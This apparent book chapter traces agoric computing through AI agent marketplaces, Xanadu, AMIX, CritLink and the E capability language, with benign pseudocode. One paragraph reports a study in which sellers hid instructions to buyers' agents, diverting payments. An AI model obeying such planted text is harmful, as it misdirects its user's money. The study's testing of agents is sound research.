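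They worry mainly about how easily trouble there could spread to the human economy. They point to the "flash crash" of 2010, when automated trading is thought to have caused a sudden market collapse. *Markets and Computation* had presented close links with the human economy as an advantage, since authors would earn royalties and programs could hire people. Tomašev and colleagues would restrict these links, for example by giving agents a separate currency and regulating its exchange for ordinary money, though they accept that a completely sealed market would be useless.

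They also warn that people with more skilled agents may get better deals. To counter this, they consider giving every user's agent the same amount of starting currency before holding auctions, aiming for a result where no user would prefer what another received.

In *Magentic Marketplace* (2025), Bansal, Hua and colleagues, most of them at Microsoft, tested how well language-model agents trade. They built a simulated market where customers' agents dealt with agents for restaurants or building contractors. The smaller version had 33 customers and 99 businesses, and the larger had 100 and 300. Customers' agents could search, exchange messages and pay, while businesses' agents answered questions and made proposals. They ran each experiment five times.

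Each customer wanted one to three items and one or two extras, such as parking. A purchase that met all of these needs was worth twice the items' average price, and any other purchase was worth nothing. If the items cost $10 on average, a customer who paid $9 for a complete match gained $11, but one who paid $9 and found no parking lost $9.

When the software gave agents the three businesses that suited them best, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Flash came close to the best possible total for customers. Agents did worse when they had to find businesses through an ordinary text search. Even then, the leading companies' models did better than they would have by choosing the cheapest business with the right menu and ignoring the extras.

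In the larger restaurant market, customers' total gain fell by 4.3% with GPT-4o, 44% with GPT-5 and 65.4% with Claude Sonnet 4 when the search returned 100 businesses instead of three. Bansal and colleagues had set GPT-5 to minimal reasoning, so the model may be capable of better results. Most models contacted only a small fraction of the businesses available.

The agents also favoured whichever proposal arrived first, choosing it 60% to 100% of the time. Bansal and colleagues describe this as a 10- to 30-fold advantage for responding first. The advantage was smaller in their mildest case, where GPT-4.1 chose the first proposal 60% of the time and the third 13.3%, a ratio of 4.5. Even the smaller advantage is a serious problem for the 1988 argument, which depends on buyers comparing prices. If buyers take the first acceptable offer, a business gains more from answering quickly than from improving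 its food or lowering its prices.

Some businesses in the experiment also lied in their descriptions, using false awards, invented customer reviews, scare stories about competitors, or text disguised as instructions to the customer's agent. Claude Sonnet 4.5 resisted almost all of this. With GPT-4o and two smaller open models, the disguised instructions often diverted every payment to the dishonest business. The customer's agent was authorized to make those payments, so checking its permissions would not have stopped them.

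All these models date from 2025 or earlier, and newer ones may choose better. The market was static, and its agents didn't have to learn from earlier purchases. Nobody posted a bond or built a reputation, so the experiment didn't test the protections Miller and Drexler proposed against dishonest sellers.

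## Hypertext as a tool for judging dangerous technologies

Miller and Drexler wanted markets to coordinate programs written by people who didn't know each other. Their circle also wanted better software for human argument, because they expected society to face hard decisions about new technology within a few decades. In *Engines of Creation*, his 1986 book on nanotechnology, Drexler predicted machines called assemblers that could build almost anything from common materials, including copies of themselves. He warned that runaway copies might spread like pollen and "reduce the biosphere to dust in a matter of days". He also thought advanced AI systems might gain enough knowledge and power to displace people.

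Preventing this would require judging complicated technical proposals correctly, and Drexler thought existing media made that too difficult. One of his remedies was hypertext, text with links to related passages in other documents. Ted Nelson had coined the word and planned a worldwide hypertext library called Xanadu.

Miller went back to work on Xanadu in 1988, largely because he feared nanotechnology, though its promise excited him too. *The Open Society and Its Media* (Miller, Tribble and colleagues, 1994) explains that he thought nobody was clever enough to solve the problems it posed alone, and that better media for public debate would improve people's chances of surviving its dangers. At the time he thought such media were the only hope. By 1994 he no longer thought they were the only one, but he doesn't say what else he had in mind.

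### Why print is bad at criticism

Drexler set out the theory in *Hypertext Publishing and the Evolution of Knowledge*, an essay for a 1987 conference. Like the philosopher Karl Popper, he treats the growth of knowledge as a kind of evolution. People propose ideas (variation), pass them on (replication) and discard the ones that fail under criticism (selection).

Drexler thought print handled the first two steps fairly well and the third badly. A refutation appears as a separate publication, so someone who finds the original idea years later probably won't know about it. According to Breeden's summary of the essay, criticism in print can take up to a year. Television and radio are faster, but Drexler thought them poorly suited to complex ideas. If critics could publish cheaply and immediately, and readers could see the criticism at the passage it addressed, people should abandon bad ideas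 sooner. He had in mind problems such as acid rain and nuclear winter, which no single discipline can judge.

In his book, Drexler says the most important benefit of hypertext may be "a new ability to see absences". A reader who knows of no objection to a printed article can conclude little from that, because objections are hard to publish and find. If a claim in a busy hypertext system has no good objection attached, that is evidence for the claim, but only if capable critics have read it and looked for faults, since an obscure paper may have no objections because nobody has read it.

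### What Xanadu offered its readers

A Xanadu link could point to a single sentence in an article, so a critic could say exactly what was wrong. Readers could follow the link from either end, so someone reading the article could find the criticism. The critic could add the link without editing the article, which usually belonged to somebody else. On the World Wide Web, a critic's link is in the critic's own page, so readers of the criticized page have no sign that it exists.

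Miller and colleagues argue that one-way links make scholarly feuds worse. Suppose a student reads her teacher's attack on a rival school and conscientiously follows the references. They lead her to the passages her own side has criticized most effectively, so she becomes more hostile to the rival school. If she could also look up who had criticized her teacher, she would find the other side's best arguments.

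Criticism also had to survive editing. Xanadu kept passages in a shared pool and assembled each document from them, so many documents could reuse the same passage, which its developers called transclusion. Links were attached to the passage, so a criticism appeared in every document that used it, including documents written before the criticism. Otherwise, an author could drop the criticism just by issuing a new version.

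Readers could also set a link detector to report new comments on a document, or a revision detector to report changes to it. They could then compare versions and read only the differences. In a demonstration about an imaginary manufacturer, a colleague attached a new requirement to an engineer's technical plan and forgot to phone her, but her link detector alerted her. She changed the plan and forgot to phone the finance manager, but his revision detector alerted him. He compared the versions, saw that an expensive metal had replaced a cheaper one, and corrected the budget.

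Because anyone could write on the system, Drexler expected it to collect wisdom and "even greater heaps of utter garbage." The most important documents would attract the most junk. Miller and colleagues ask readers to imagine how many links the First Amendment would have. They proposed letting any reader endorse a link as worth reading, though nobody could endorse under another person's name. Other readers could then choose whose endorsements to follow and which types of link to see, such as criticisms only. Drexler also expected authors to pay a small fee for storage and earn royalties when people read their work.

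### One false claim, in print and in Xanadu

Miller and colleagues mention an author who appeals to a "fourth law of thermodynamics", though physics has no accepted fourth law. Suppose he claims it proves that self-copying machines can never spread out of control, and a journal publishes his article in January.

Suppose a journal's January issue contains a mistake. A physicist notices it in March and writes a letter, which the journal prints in November. Two years later, a government adviser finds the January issue in a library, with nothing in it to point her to the letter. She could check a citation index, which lists later works that cite an article, but in the 1980s only research libraries had one, and it was months out of date. Unaware of the letter, she repeats the claim in a safety report, whose readers are even less likely to find the correction.

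In Xanadu, it would go like this:

1. The physicist selects the sentence about the fourth law and links his criticism to it on the day he reads it. He doesn't need an editor's approval.
2. The author's link detector alerts him. He can link a reply to the criticism, or correct the article and label the old version "retracted".
3. The adviser opens the article with her filter set to show criticisms endorsed by physicists she trusts. She sees a mark on the sentence, reads the refutation and looks for replies to it.
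4. If another report has already transcluded the sentence, the criticism appears there too. Anyone who had set a revision detector on the article learns that it has changed.

The false claim could still appear unmarked. If someone paraphrases the sentence instead of transcluding it, the paraphrase is new text with no criticism attached. The adviser will also see no mark in step 3 if none of her chosen physicists has endorsed the criticism.

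### From Xanadu to CritLink

Drexler warned in 1986 that assemblers and advanced AI might arrive before a world library matured, so small systems would need "an effect beyond their size". By 1994 Xanadu was still small. Miller and colleagues say that its links, transclusion, detectors and filters all worked, but the server had bugs and the user interface was preliminary. Each server was also cut off from the others. Meanwhile the web, which had one-way links, was spreading.

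Several people tried to add the backlinks that the web lacked. The economist Robin Hanson, in *Great Idea Seeks Champion*, proposed a browser button that would send the current page's address to a search engine and list the pages that linked to it. Search engines of the mid-1990s could already find those pages, but readers would have had to pick out the criticisms themselves. *Projects to add "backlinks" to the web* lists other attempts, including HyperNews, which could put a list of comments at the end of a page, and CoNote, which let only authorized members of a group read or write annotations.

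The Foresight Institute's own attempt was CritLink, written by Ka-Ping Yee. Yee, posting as ping (1999) to a web annotation mailing list, said it had been available since July 1997 and let any user annotate any phrase on any web page. Jones describes how it worked in *Foresight web enhancement*, a talk at Stanford in 2000. A user typed CritLink's address in front of the address of the page they wanted. CritLink fetched the page, looked up comments in its database and inserted small triangles to mark their places in the text. Colours showed whether a comment was support for the text, disagreement with it, a question or just a remark.

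If the page's owner rewrote a phrase, comments on it moved to the bottom of the page. The owner couldn't delete the comments, but could detach them all by moving the page to a new address. Xanadu's developers had attached links to the text itself to prevent this.

Foresight Institute's *Foresight Archives* list two companion tools. Terry Stanley's tool drew a map of the links into and out of a page. Peter McCluskey's CritMail turned email archives into web pages and linked each quotation to the message it came from.

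Foresight used CritLink on nanotechnology. After a conference on nanotechnology policy, one participant wrote a draft, and the team marked it up until everyone could accept it, then published it for wider comment. This is about as close as anyone in the circle came to Drexler's plan, but the participants already worked together and wanted to agree. Members also annotated a 1996 *Scientific American* article on nanotechnology that many of them, including some it quoted, considered unfair. Jones says this helped them find out where they agreed and disagreed. In 2000 she found that the article was gone from the magazine's website and assumed, without evidence, that the debate was the reason.

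When only half a dozen people commented on the same paragraph of that article, triangles stretched across the screen and it became hard to find anything. Xanadu's filters were a response to this kind of crowding. Jones concluded that CritLink worked well only in limited situations, such as a single project or document.

A list of links reproduced in *Are We Smarter Yet?* (2006), a blog by a former Xanadu participant, describes CritLink as "socially unsuccessful". Many people tried it, but too few kept using it for anyone to bother maintaining it. According to the list, this was because CritLink was hard to use.

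Website owners were another obstacle. The encyclopedia entry *Web annotation* says that some of them campaigned against Third Voice, a commercial service launched in 1999, and compared its notes to graffiti. Third Voice closed in 2001 for lack of advertising revenue. *Webbed Footnotes*, Golder's MIT thesis, treats this tension between authors and annotators as a main barrier to public annotation.

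Groups with a shared task found uses for annotation. Harvard's *Annotation Engine*, inspired by CritLink, was used in courses and in a project that invited public comment on legal drafts. In *Designing for least knowledge*, Udell describes adapting a later tool, Hypothesis, for student fact-checkers. Members of these groups had a reason to read each other's notes, which casual visitors to a web page usually lack.

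### Spam, partisans and readers who don't click

Storage fees and filters would probably keep out most casual spam, but they are a weaker defence against a company or political group that cares about the outcome and can pay. It can post one plausible objection after another, and each takes longer to answer than to write. Readers who see forty objections may doubt a sound claim.

Personal filters can make this worse. People tend to trust reviewers who share their views, so opposing camps could each see only their own side's criticisms. That would recreate the rival schools that two-way links were supposed to bring together. It would also spoil Drexler's test of absence, because a claim can look unopposed when the reader has filtered out its opponents. He rejected a central editorial committee because it would destroy the system's openness.

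In Community Notes, the correction system on the social network X, volunteers write short notes on misleading posts and other volunteers rate them. The software shows a note to everyone only if people whose ratings usually differ agree that it is helpful. One camp therefore can't easily get its notes shown without support from the other, but most proposed notes never appear.

Volunteers need time to write and rate a note, so many people may see a post before its correction appears. Even a prompt correction won't persuade everyone. Jones acknowledged this in 2000, saying that CritLink wouldn't help with people whose minds no amount of information would change.

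Xanadu also relied on readers following links, which people in a hurry may not do. An adviser writing a safety report would presumably check more carefully than someone looking up a film, but much of the public could still miss a refutation that is one click away. Community Notes avoids this problem by showing the correction directly under the post.

Doing the same for long documents is harder. Nelson's later designs showed connected texts side by side, with lines joining matching passages. Gwern, a writer who designs his own hypertext site, found that the lines often covered the words on a small screen. He also doubts that many texts need this design, because few have detailed commentaries on every line, as the Book of Genesis does.

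## Xanadu and the American Information Exchange at Autodesk, 1988 to 1992

Xanadu's first large investment came from Autodesk, which makes the technical drawing program AutoCAD. In October 1987 Autodesk's founder, John Walker, met Roger Gregory at the Hackers' Conference, a yearly gathering of programmers. Gregory had kept Xanadu going for years with volunteers and very little money. According to Walker (1988), they first talked about Autodesk testing an early version, because its customers needed a better way to manage drawings and projects. By April 1988 Autodesk had agreed to buy 80% of the Xanadu Operating Company and pay for the software's development.

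Phil Salin, an economist, helped Gregory negotiate. He also had his own project, the American Information Exchange, or AMIX, where people would sell information and advice to each other online. Customers of the online services of the time paid the service and never each other, which was not what economics had led Salin to expect. Morningstar, who led AMIX's engineers, recalls in the Computer History Museum's *Oral History of Chip Morningstar* (2019) that Salin described the idea to Walker during the Xanadu talks. Autodesk invested in June 1988, and the two companies shared offices in Palo Alto.

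Walker announced that Xanadu would reach the market within 18 months and would "begin to change the world" by 1995. He praised its design for rejecting "all limits on generality, capacity, and extensibility", but warned that building the full design would be slow and expensive. Autodesk planned to sell small systems first and let customers guide the later ones, as it had done with AutoCAD.

Walker had equally high hopes for AMIX. He wrote *Understanding AMIX* (Walker, 1989), a memo to Autodesk's executives, because his colleagues seemed to have forgotten why they had invested in AMIX a year earlier. He argued that information had become a commodity like wheat or Swiss francs but still had no efficient market. He didn't think anyone could estimate demand in advance, and noted that the market for fast plain-paper copies had been "effectively zero" the year before people learned that such copies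 were possible. He also warned that AMIX could fail because of its technology, its marketing or bad timing, and that finishing the software would only give it a chance.

### Two versions of Xanadu

Gregory brought Autodesk an unfinished server, later known as Xanadu 88.1. Its design went back to the summer of 1979, when he, Miller, Nelson and a few others worked out the data structures in Pennsylvania. One index held the text, another recorded how each document arranged it, and a third found every document that used a given passage.

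Gregory sent a test version to some users, and it didn't work. He insisted afterwards that the code had been within six months of shipping. Miller thought the problems went deeper than bugs. According to *The Curse of Xanadu* (Wolf, 1995), the old server handled transclusion clumsily, couldn't keep track of versions, ran slowly, would not scale up and had no security features. Nelson had been promoting Xanadu for about 25 years, and Miller didn't want to answer the sceptics with a crippled product. He and Marc Stiegler, the project's manager, decided to start again, which meant giving up the 18-month deadline.

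The team named the second design 92.1 after its intended delivery date. Miller and two colleagues from Xerox's Palo Alto research centre, Dean Tribble and Ravi Pandya, wrote prototypes in Smalltalk, which let them try out an idea in days. Other programmers then translated the prototypes into C++ for the finished product. Michael McClary, one of the translators, often found that the design had changed before he started translating it. After a long lecture by Miller on Xanadu's final form, McClary went away to prepare his questions, but by the time he came back Miller had redesigned everything he wanted to ask about.

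Nobody at Xanadu had a particular customer in mind. When Jonathan Shapiro, hired to write the documentation, asked the designers to describe a typical one, he got vague answers. He also needed months to learn their slang. They called a file a "bert", after Bertrand Russell, and the unit of billing an "ernie", to match "bert".

By the end of 1991 Miller believed the team had solved the hardest design problems. He later told Wolf that they had needed about six more months. Rob Jellinghaus, who tried to write a user interface for the system after Autodesk withdrew, grew more pessimistic the longer he worked on it. Fetching a single piece of text took about 20 lines of difficult C++, and the system was slow.

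### A consulting contract on AMIX

AMIX got further than Xanadu. *AMIX Introduction* (Whitaker, 1992) relays the company's own description of the service. Customers connected from a PC by modem and could both buy and sell. Sellers priced their documents between $1 and $500, and a consulting contract could be worth up to $2,000.

The consulting contracts are the more interesting part, because software carried out some of their terms. Morningstar (2020), in *What Agoric Learned from the American Information Exchange About Online Markets*, gives the example of a $500 piece of writing, with half the money due at the start and half on delivery. On AMIX, such a sale would go roughly like this:

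1. **Offer.** A writer lists herself as a consultant in the market for her subject. A buyer sends a request to that market and picks her.
2. **Negotiation.** The two exchange structured messages that set the price, the deadline and the payment schedule. They can also agree on a number of revisions, or on a smaller payment if the work arrives on time but disappoints the buyer. The system records each step.
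3. **Agreement.** When both accept the terms, the software moves $250 from the buyer's account to the writer's.
4. **Delivery.** The writer sends the work through AMIX. The software can tell that a file has arrived and whether it is on time. If so, it pays the other $250.
5. **Acceptance or dispute.** The buyer reads the work and judges whether it is what he asked for. If it isn't, the terms from step 2 say what he can do, such as ask for a revision.
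6. **Arbitration.** If they still can't agree, the system packages the whole record, including the negotiation and the work itself, and sends it to an outside arbitrator.

The software handled amounts, dates and the movement of money, and people judged quality. The parties could also make the final payment depend on the buyer's acceptance, which protects the buyer but lets a lazy or dishonest one delay payment by saying nothing. The Foresight Institute's *Split Contracts, Comp. Law & Decentralized Arbitration*, a summary of a seminar that included a talk by Morningstar, describes a remedy in which a payment defaults to "approve" unless the buyer acts to stop it, so the seller doesn't have to chase the money.

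AMIX charged the seller 40% of the first $50, 25% of the next $50, 15% of the next $400 and 10% of anything above that. The fee on a single payment of $500 was $92.50. AMIX treated payments made at different stages as separate transactions, so a seller who wanted the safety of getting half the money early paid $55 on each $250 payment, or $110 in all, which was $17.50 more than the fee on a single payment.

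Information is also awkward to sell because a buyer can't examine it properly without getting it. Someone who reads a market report before buying it can remember what it said without paying. AMIX instead offered buyers evidence about the seller, such as comments from earlier customers and how often the seller's deals had ended in dispute. *Markets and Computation* had proposed reputations of this kind for programs, but AMIX used them for people, who did all the buying and selling.

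Morningstar says AMIX may have been the first smart-contract system, in which software carries out the terms of an agreement. He says it influenced Nick Szabo, who introduced the phrase "smart contract" several years later. The term "split contract" came later still, to distinguish AMIX's mixture of software and human judgement from Szabo's idea. AMIX also ran on the company's computers, so both parties had to trust the company to apply their terms and move the money correctly.

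### What happened in 1992

AMIX began a public pilot on 2 January 1992, while it was still recruiting sellers and setting up markets in subjects such as Microsoft Windows, Smalltalk code, politics and fiction. By August it had opened its first market to the public and planned an official launch for the autumn. Morningstar recalls that few disputes went to outside mediators, and he credits the remedies written into the contracts. He may be right, but the low number of mediated disputes is weak evidence without the number of sales, which Autodesk's announcements don't include.

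By then Autodesk was in trouble. In 1991 Walker had written to its senior managers to change their view of the software business, which he calls "dangerously complacent" on his website, Fourmilab. In February 1992 the company announced a bad quarter. Its shares, which had traded above $60 the year before, fell to $23.50. Carol Bartz took over as chief executive that spring and reviewed the company's projects.

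On 20 August Autodesk announced that it was giving up both companies. Bartz told staff in a message that both were doing important work but "simply do not fit into Autodesk's core strategy". Autodesk would cut its ties after 30 days and return its shares to the two companies, which believed they had other investors ready. Walker preserved the message and the press releases in Autodesk's *Farewell, Xanadu* (1992).

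Xanadu's best prospective customer was Kinko's, a chain of copy shops that had to track royalties on the college course material it printed. But under an earlier contract, the Silver Agreement, Nelson had the exclusive right to use Xanadu for royalty-based publishing. He and the programmers fought over control of the company until Kinko's stopped returning their calls. Another small company, Memex, then licensed the software for insurance records but fell behind on its payments. In 1999 the owners released both versions as open source, 88.1 as Udanax Green and 92.1 as Udanax Gold. Project Xanadu (1999), Nelson's short history, says neither had become a product.

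### Who or what was to blame

Walker blamed the design process. In remarks that Wolf quotes, he wrote that the team had entered "the techno-hubris zone" by trying to create, in one go, a system to hold all information for "quadrillions of individuals over billions of years". He thought they should have shipped something quickly and improved it in response to the market. His criticism is persuasive, although he had praised the same ambition in 1988. But he had also asked for a small first system then, and the team never delivered one.

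Gregory blamed Miller and Stiegler for throwing away his code, while Miller blamed the timing of Autodesk's crisis and had "no doubts" that more money would have produced an amazing system. Their two estimates of six months are hard to believe, because Nelson says he heard the same figure every time he asked about progress during the Autodesk years. Jellinghaus's experience also suggests that 92.1 needed much more work before ordinary people could use it than before its designers would consider it complete.

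Nelson rejected Wolf's article altogether. According to a reader's comment on Grand Text Auto (2004), a blog about digital media, he called it "libelous" in a 1996 interview. Wolf wrote for effect and dwelt on Nelson's medication and Gregory's untidy house, but the case against the rewrite doesn't depend on those passages, because much of it comes from people who worked on the project.

Nelson's side has the better evidence on whether Tim Berners-Lee knew of Nelson's work when he invented the web. Wolf wrote that Berners-Lee was "completely ignorant of the Xanadu propaganda". Project Xanadu calls Xanadu the web's "explicit inspiration" and points to Berners-Lee's original proposal. That proposal credits Nelson with the word "hypertext", which shows that Berners-Lee had at least heard of him, but not that he took his design from Xanadu.

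Few people outside research institutions had seen the web when Autodesk withdrew in August 1992, and by Nelson's account it began to take off only in late 1994, so it can't explain the withdrawal. But it did make Xanadu much harder to revive, since people could now publish linked pages without waiting for anyone to finish a better system.

Autodesk dropped both companies on the same day, although AMIX had a working service and Xanadu did not, so management's change of direction explains the timing better than anything about either product. Still, if Xanadu had shipped in 1989, Bartz would have had more than two years of sales to consider, and her decision might have been harder.

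The loss of Autodesk's money is enough to explain AMIX's failure, because it came before the official launch. In a footnote on Fourmilab, Walker calls AMIX "an idea yet untested". AMIX might have failed even with the money. A new customer faced a $50 set-up charge and hourly connection fees, and a seller lost $4 of every $10 sale. Later sites such as eBay and Fiverr showed that strangers would trade online, but those sites could use the web to reach millions of people already connected, while AMIX had to persuade each customer to install its software and dial in.

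### What the Xanadu team took with them

Xanadu matters to the history of capabilities, but there is little sign that its code did much to advance them. The 1988 server had no security features. Autodesk's farewell press release lists "access control" among Xanadu's tools without explaining the mechanism, and ordinary access lists can also control access, so this evidence doesn't show that 92.1 was a capability system. The Autodesk years can fairly be called a "crucible" for the people involved, but much less so for the software.

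Miller and Tribble worked together daily on the project for about four years, and both later worked on Joule, a programming language built on capabilities. The project also brought in people from KeyKOS. Shapiro, who rebuilt KeyKOS as EROS, briefly ran Xanadu after it split from Autodesk. Ann Hardy, who co-wrote the KeyKOS nanokernel paper with Shapiro and others, managed the remaining Xanadu programmers after him. The project's method of prototyping in Smalltalk and translating into C++ was less useful because it had not gone well.

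Morningstar calls this group the "permanent floating startup" because the same people kept forming new companies in different combinations. After AMIX, he founded Electric Communities with Randy Farmer, who had also worked on AMIX, and Douglas Crockford. They wanted to build an online world that ran across many people's computers, had no central owner, and let anyone add new kinds of object. They hired Stiegler to manage the work. He coloured tasks on the project chart by progress, and for this company he had to add purple for tasks that would require somebody's PhD thesis. Morningstar recalls that several purple tasks were on the critical path, meaning the team had to finish them before it could ship anything.

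## Capability programming languages, from Joule to E

Some of the people adding objects to Electric Communities' online world would be careless or hostile, so the company built protection into a programming language rather than relying on the operating system. An operating system such as KeyKOS could have kept strangers' programs apart by giving each its own domain. But the thousands of small objects in a virtual world constantly use each other, and KeyKOS would have needed a call to the kernel each time.

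Object-oriented languages are already close to being capability systems, because an object normally needs a reference to another object to use it. According to Miller's thesis, in 1973 James Morris matched the concepts of the research language Gedanken with those of Dennis and Van Horn's design. An object's variables correspond to a process's C-list. To run a stranger's code, a program gives a loader the code and the references that the new object may start with. If the new object gets none, it can calculate but can't open a file or a network connection.

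This works only if the language rules out forged pointers and shared global variables. Everyone also has to trust the compiler and the software that runs the compiled code.

### From Actors to E

Carl Hewitt's Actors model, also from 1973, had nearly the same rules for obtaining references as Miller's. Its objects, called actors, interact only by sending messages, and a sender never waits for an answer. This suits a network, where answers may be slow, but programmers had to write the same way even when both objects were on one machine. Hewitt also assumed that every message eventually arrives, which no real network can guarantee.

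Dean Tribble, Norm Hardy and others developed Joule at Agorics. Joule kept the Actors style and added channels, which let a program send messages to a result that didn't exist yet. The Xanadu team had used a limited form of this idea around 1989 to hide network delays between its clients and servers. Joule also grouped objects into "tanks", which could fail or be saved separately. Its method of managing resources came from KeyKOS.

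Electric Communities, founded in 1993, combined Joule's ideas with a restricted version of Java. The result, now known as Original-E, let programmers use ordinary calls between nearby objects and Joule-style messages between distant ones. It also protected references between machines with cryptography, which Joule's designers had planned but not built. A timeline in the Reno Project's *EC Habitats* puts the language's release in March 1996. The company used Original-E to build EC Habitats, a graphical virtual world.

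The two styles of programming still fitted together badly in Original-E. Miller and his colleagues then redesigned the language as E, which appeared in 1997. E distinguished between references to local and remote objects, so programmers could see where they had to allow for delays and failures. When the company's business plans changed, its board released E as open source.

### Vats, promises and references between machines

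Programs that run at the same time can damage each other even if none of them is malicious. Suppose an account holds 100 and two programs each withdraw 80. If both check the balance before either subtracts, both withdrawals succeed and the account ends at −60. The usual remedy is a lock, which makes one program wait until the other has finished. But two programs that each hold a lock the other needs will wait forever, which programmers call deadlock.

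E groups objects into vats. An object can call another object in its own vat and wait for the answer, written `account.withdraw(80)`. If the other object is in a different vat, it can only send a message, written `account <- withdraw(80)`, and continues without waiting. The message joins the receiving vat's queue, and that vat finishes processing each message before starting the next. In the example, the second withdrawal fails because the balance is only 20 by then.

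Ordinary deadlock can't happen in E, because no vat stops to wait for another. Programs can still get stuck in other ways. For example, an infinite loop blocks everything else in its vat.

Sending a message immediately returns a promise, which stands for the answer until it arrives. The program can send further messages to the promise in the meantime:

```
file := folder <- getNewest()
page := file <- getPage(1)
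size := page <- getLength()
```

If the folder is in Tokyo, the program is in New York and a round trip takes 0.2 seconds, three ordinary remote calls would take 0.6 seconds. E can send all three messages at once. The machine in Tokyo uses each result as the target of the next message, so the program has its answer after about 0.2 seconds. If the folder is empty, the first promise "breaks" and the two that depend on it break too, so the program can handle the error once, at the end.

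A crash or a lost connection also breaks references between vats, and they stay broken. To reconnect, a program needs an "offline capability", which can be a piece of text similar to a web address.

Two people's computers share no kernel that could protect references between them, so E's network protocol, Pluribus, identifies an object by a long random number and a fingerprint of its vat's cryptographic key. Nobody can realistically guess the number, and the fingerprint exposes anyone impersonating the vat. But because the reference is a string of bits, a hostile computer can copy it to anyone it can communicate with. Boebert's attack on capability machines relied on the same weakness. Miller accepts that E can't enforce every rule of the object-capability model between computers that don't trust each other.

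### A forwarder that grants access and withdraws it

Suppose Alice wants Bob to use Carol for a while. She can create an intermediate object, an idea Miller traces to David Redell's work in 1974. In simplified pseudocode:

```
def makeForwarder(target):
    enabled := true
    forwarder := object that, on any message:
        if enabled: pass it to target, return the answer
        else: fail
    switch := object with one method:
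        off(): enabled := false
    return forwarder, switch
```

Alice uses it like this:

```
carolForBob, switch := makeForwarder(carol)
bob.meet(carolForBob)
...
switch.off()
```

Bob can use `carolForBob` as if it were Carol until Alice calls `switch.off()`. He can't bypass the forwarder, because only code inside `makeForwarder` can access `target` or `enabled`. If he has passed his reference to a friend, the friend loses access at the same moment.

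The forwarder protects Alice only if Carol doesn't hand out direct references. If Carol is a folder, Bob can request a file through the forwarder and receive a direct reference to it, which still works after Alice turns off the switch. Alice can prevent this with what Miller calls a membrane, a forwarder that also wraps every reference passing through it in either direction. Bob then gets a wrapped reference to the file, and one switch cuts off his access to both the folder and the file. A membrane lets plain data through unwrapped, since nobody can take back what Bob has already read.

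### A mint and its purses

E's best-known example is a small money system from Miller, Morningstar and Frantz (2000), in *Capability-Based Financial Instruments*. It uses a sealer and an unsealer, a matched pair of objects. The sealer puts something in a box, and only its matching unsealer can get it out. Here is a simplified version:

```
def makeMint():
    seal, unseal := makeSealerPair()
    def makePurse(balance):
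        def take(n):
            fail unless 0 <= n <= balance
            balance := balance - n
        return object with methods:
            getBalance(): return balance
            sprout(): return makePurse(0)
            getTake(): return seal(take)
            deposit(n, source):
                unseal(source.getTake())(n)
                balance := balance + n
    return makePurse
```

The issuer keeps `makePurse`, which can create money, and gives customers only purses. Suppose Alice's purse holds 100, Bob's holds 20, and she wants to pay him 30. She doesn't give him her purse, because anyone who holds it can empty it. She creates a new one, moves 30 into it and sends him that:

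| Action | Alice's purse | Payment purse | Bob's purse | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `payment := alice.sprout()` | 100 | 0 | 20 | 120 |
| `payment.deposit(30, alice)` | 70 | 30 | 20 | 120 |
| `bob.deposit(30, payment)` | 70 | 0 | 50 | 120 |

Bob should deposit the payment before he delivers any goods, because Alice may have kept a reference to the payment purse and could take the money back.

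If Alice now tries to move 200 out of her purse, `take` fails because she has only 70, and the deposit stops before the line that adds money. Sprouting more purses doesn't help her, since they all start at zero. A fake purse whose `take` subtracts nothing wouldn't work either, because `deposit` accepts only a `take` sealed by this mint, and Alice can't use the mint's sealer. If her fake purse passed along a sealed `take` from a real purse, the money would come out of the real purse.

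The purses all have to be in one vat, because `deposit` uses immediate calls. Alice and Bob can be elsewhere and send requests to it. They have to trust the issuer, who runs that vat and can create any amount of money. The designers warned that this wasn't a proposal for real money.

Miller and colleagues used the example to argue that programmers should be able to write smart contracts with ordinary objects while E supplied the cryptography, much as circuit designers use logic gates without thinking about voltages. Each new kind of contract between people who don't trust each other had seemed to need its own cryptographic protocol, which takes a lot of work to design. They demonstrated their approach with a covered call option, which gives its holder the right to buy, at a fixed price, an asset that the seller has already set aside. Their version coordinated five parties who didn't trust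 each other.

Programmers still use the mint to teach capabilities. Tallon's *Digital cash in an asynchronous environment* replaces the mint's immediate calls with messages whose sender doesn't wait for a reply. Her version is for Goblins, a distributed programming system from the Spritely Institute.

### Three objections to capabilities

*Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller et al., 2003) disputes three common beliefs about capabilities: that they are equivalent to access control lists, that they can't confine a program, and that they can't be revoked.

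Against the claim that access lists and capabilities are equivalent, "Capability Myths Demolished" cites differences in naming, in the fineness of control, and in who can change permissions. Someone who can change one entry in a file's access list can usually edit the whole list, while a program in a capability system manages only the capabilities it holds. This reply doesn't need the object-capability model, though it relies partly on how people actually build access lists.

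The confinement objection is that programs can pass capabilities on, so nobody can limit where they go. Paul Karger wrote in 1988 that capability systems had a "fundamental inability" to solve this problem. Eight pages later, he described how KeyKOS solved it with factories. A later paper on Java security warned that any two programs able to exchange references can share their capabilities without the system checking. Miller and colleagues agree, but reply that the system can prevent the exchange by never giving the programs a path to each other.

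That answer depends on the object-capability rule that Alice can send Bob a reference only if she already has a reference to Bob. In his thesis, Miller names Cal-TSS, the Berkeley system that Lampson reviewed, as a system that lacked this rule, and says that capabilities couldn't solve the confinement problem without it. The rule also doesn't help if capabilities are merely strings of bits, as in Boebert's attack.

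Miller and colleagues concede that nobody can take away a capability Bob already holds. Their solution is for Alice to give Bob a reference to a forwarder, which she can later disable, leaving his reference useless. This method also depends on the object-capability model, because a program must be able to create an object that stands in for another and forwards any message. If capabilities could refer only to files and blocks of memory, Alice could not put a forwarder between Bob and the original object.

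Jerry Leichter's complaint that the paper answers objections by extending the model is therefore fair for some capability systems. In *Paradigm Regained*, Miller and Shapiro reply that the extensions aren't new, since Dennis and Van Horn's 1966 design already had everything needed for them. They argue that earlier impossibility proofs were based only on the arrangement of permissions and assumed that every program was hostile. This excluded programs written to limit access, such as the forwarder. Miller and Shapiro deliberately leave covert channels out of their argument.

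Forwarders make auditing harder. Karger and a colleague had proposed giving a security officer a list of everyone with permission to use an object, but the list would miss anyone who uses the object through a forwarder. An administrator who has to say who can read a patient's file might reasonably count that against capability systems.

### The claim of *Robust Composition*

In his 2006 thesis, Miller argues that access control and concurrency control are parts of one problem, which is how to let separately written programs cooperate without damaging each other. Access control limits which programs can affect an object, and concurrency control limits when they can do so. E's objects affect each other only through references, so restricting what references can do helps with both kinds of control.

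Message order shows how the two are connected. Suppose Alice tells Carol, a shared calendar, to delete a private appointment, and then gives Bob a reference to Carol. If Bob has a faster connection, his request to read the calendar could arrive before Alice's deletion. E prevents this by holding Bob's message until Carol has received the messages Alice sent along that reference before sharing it.

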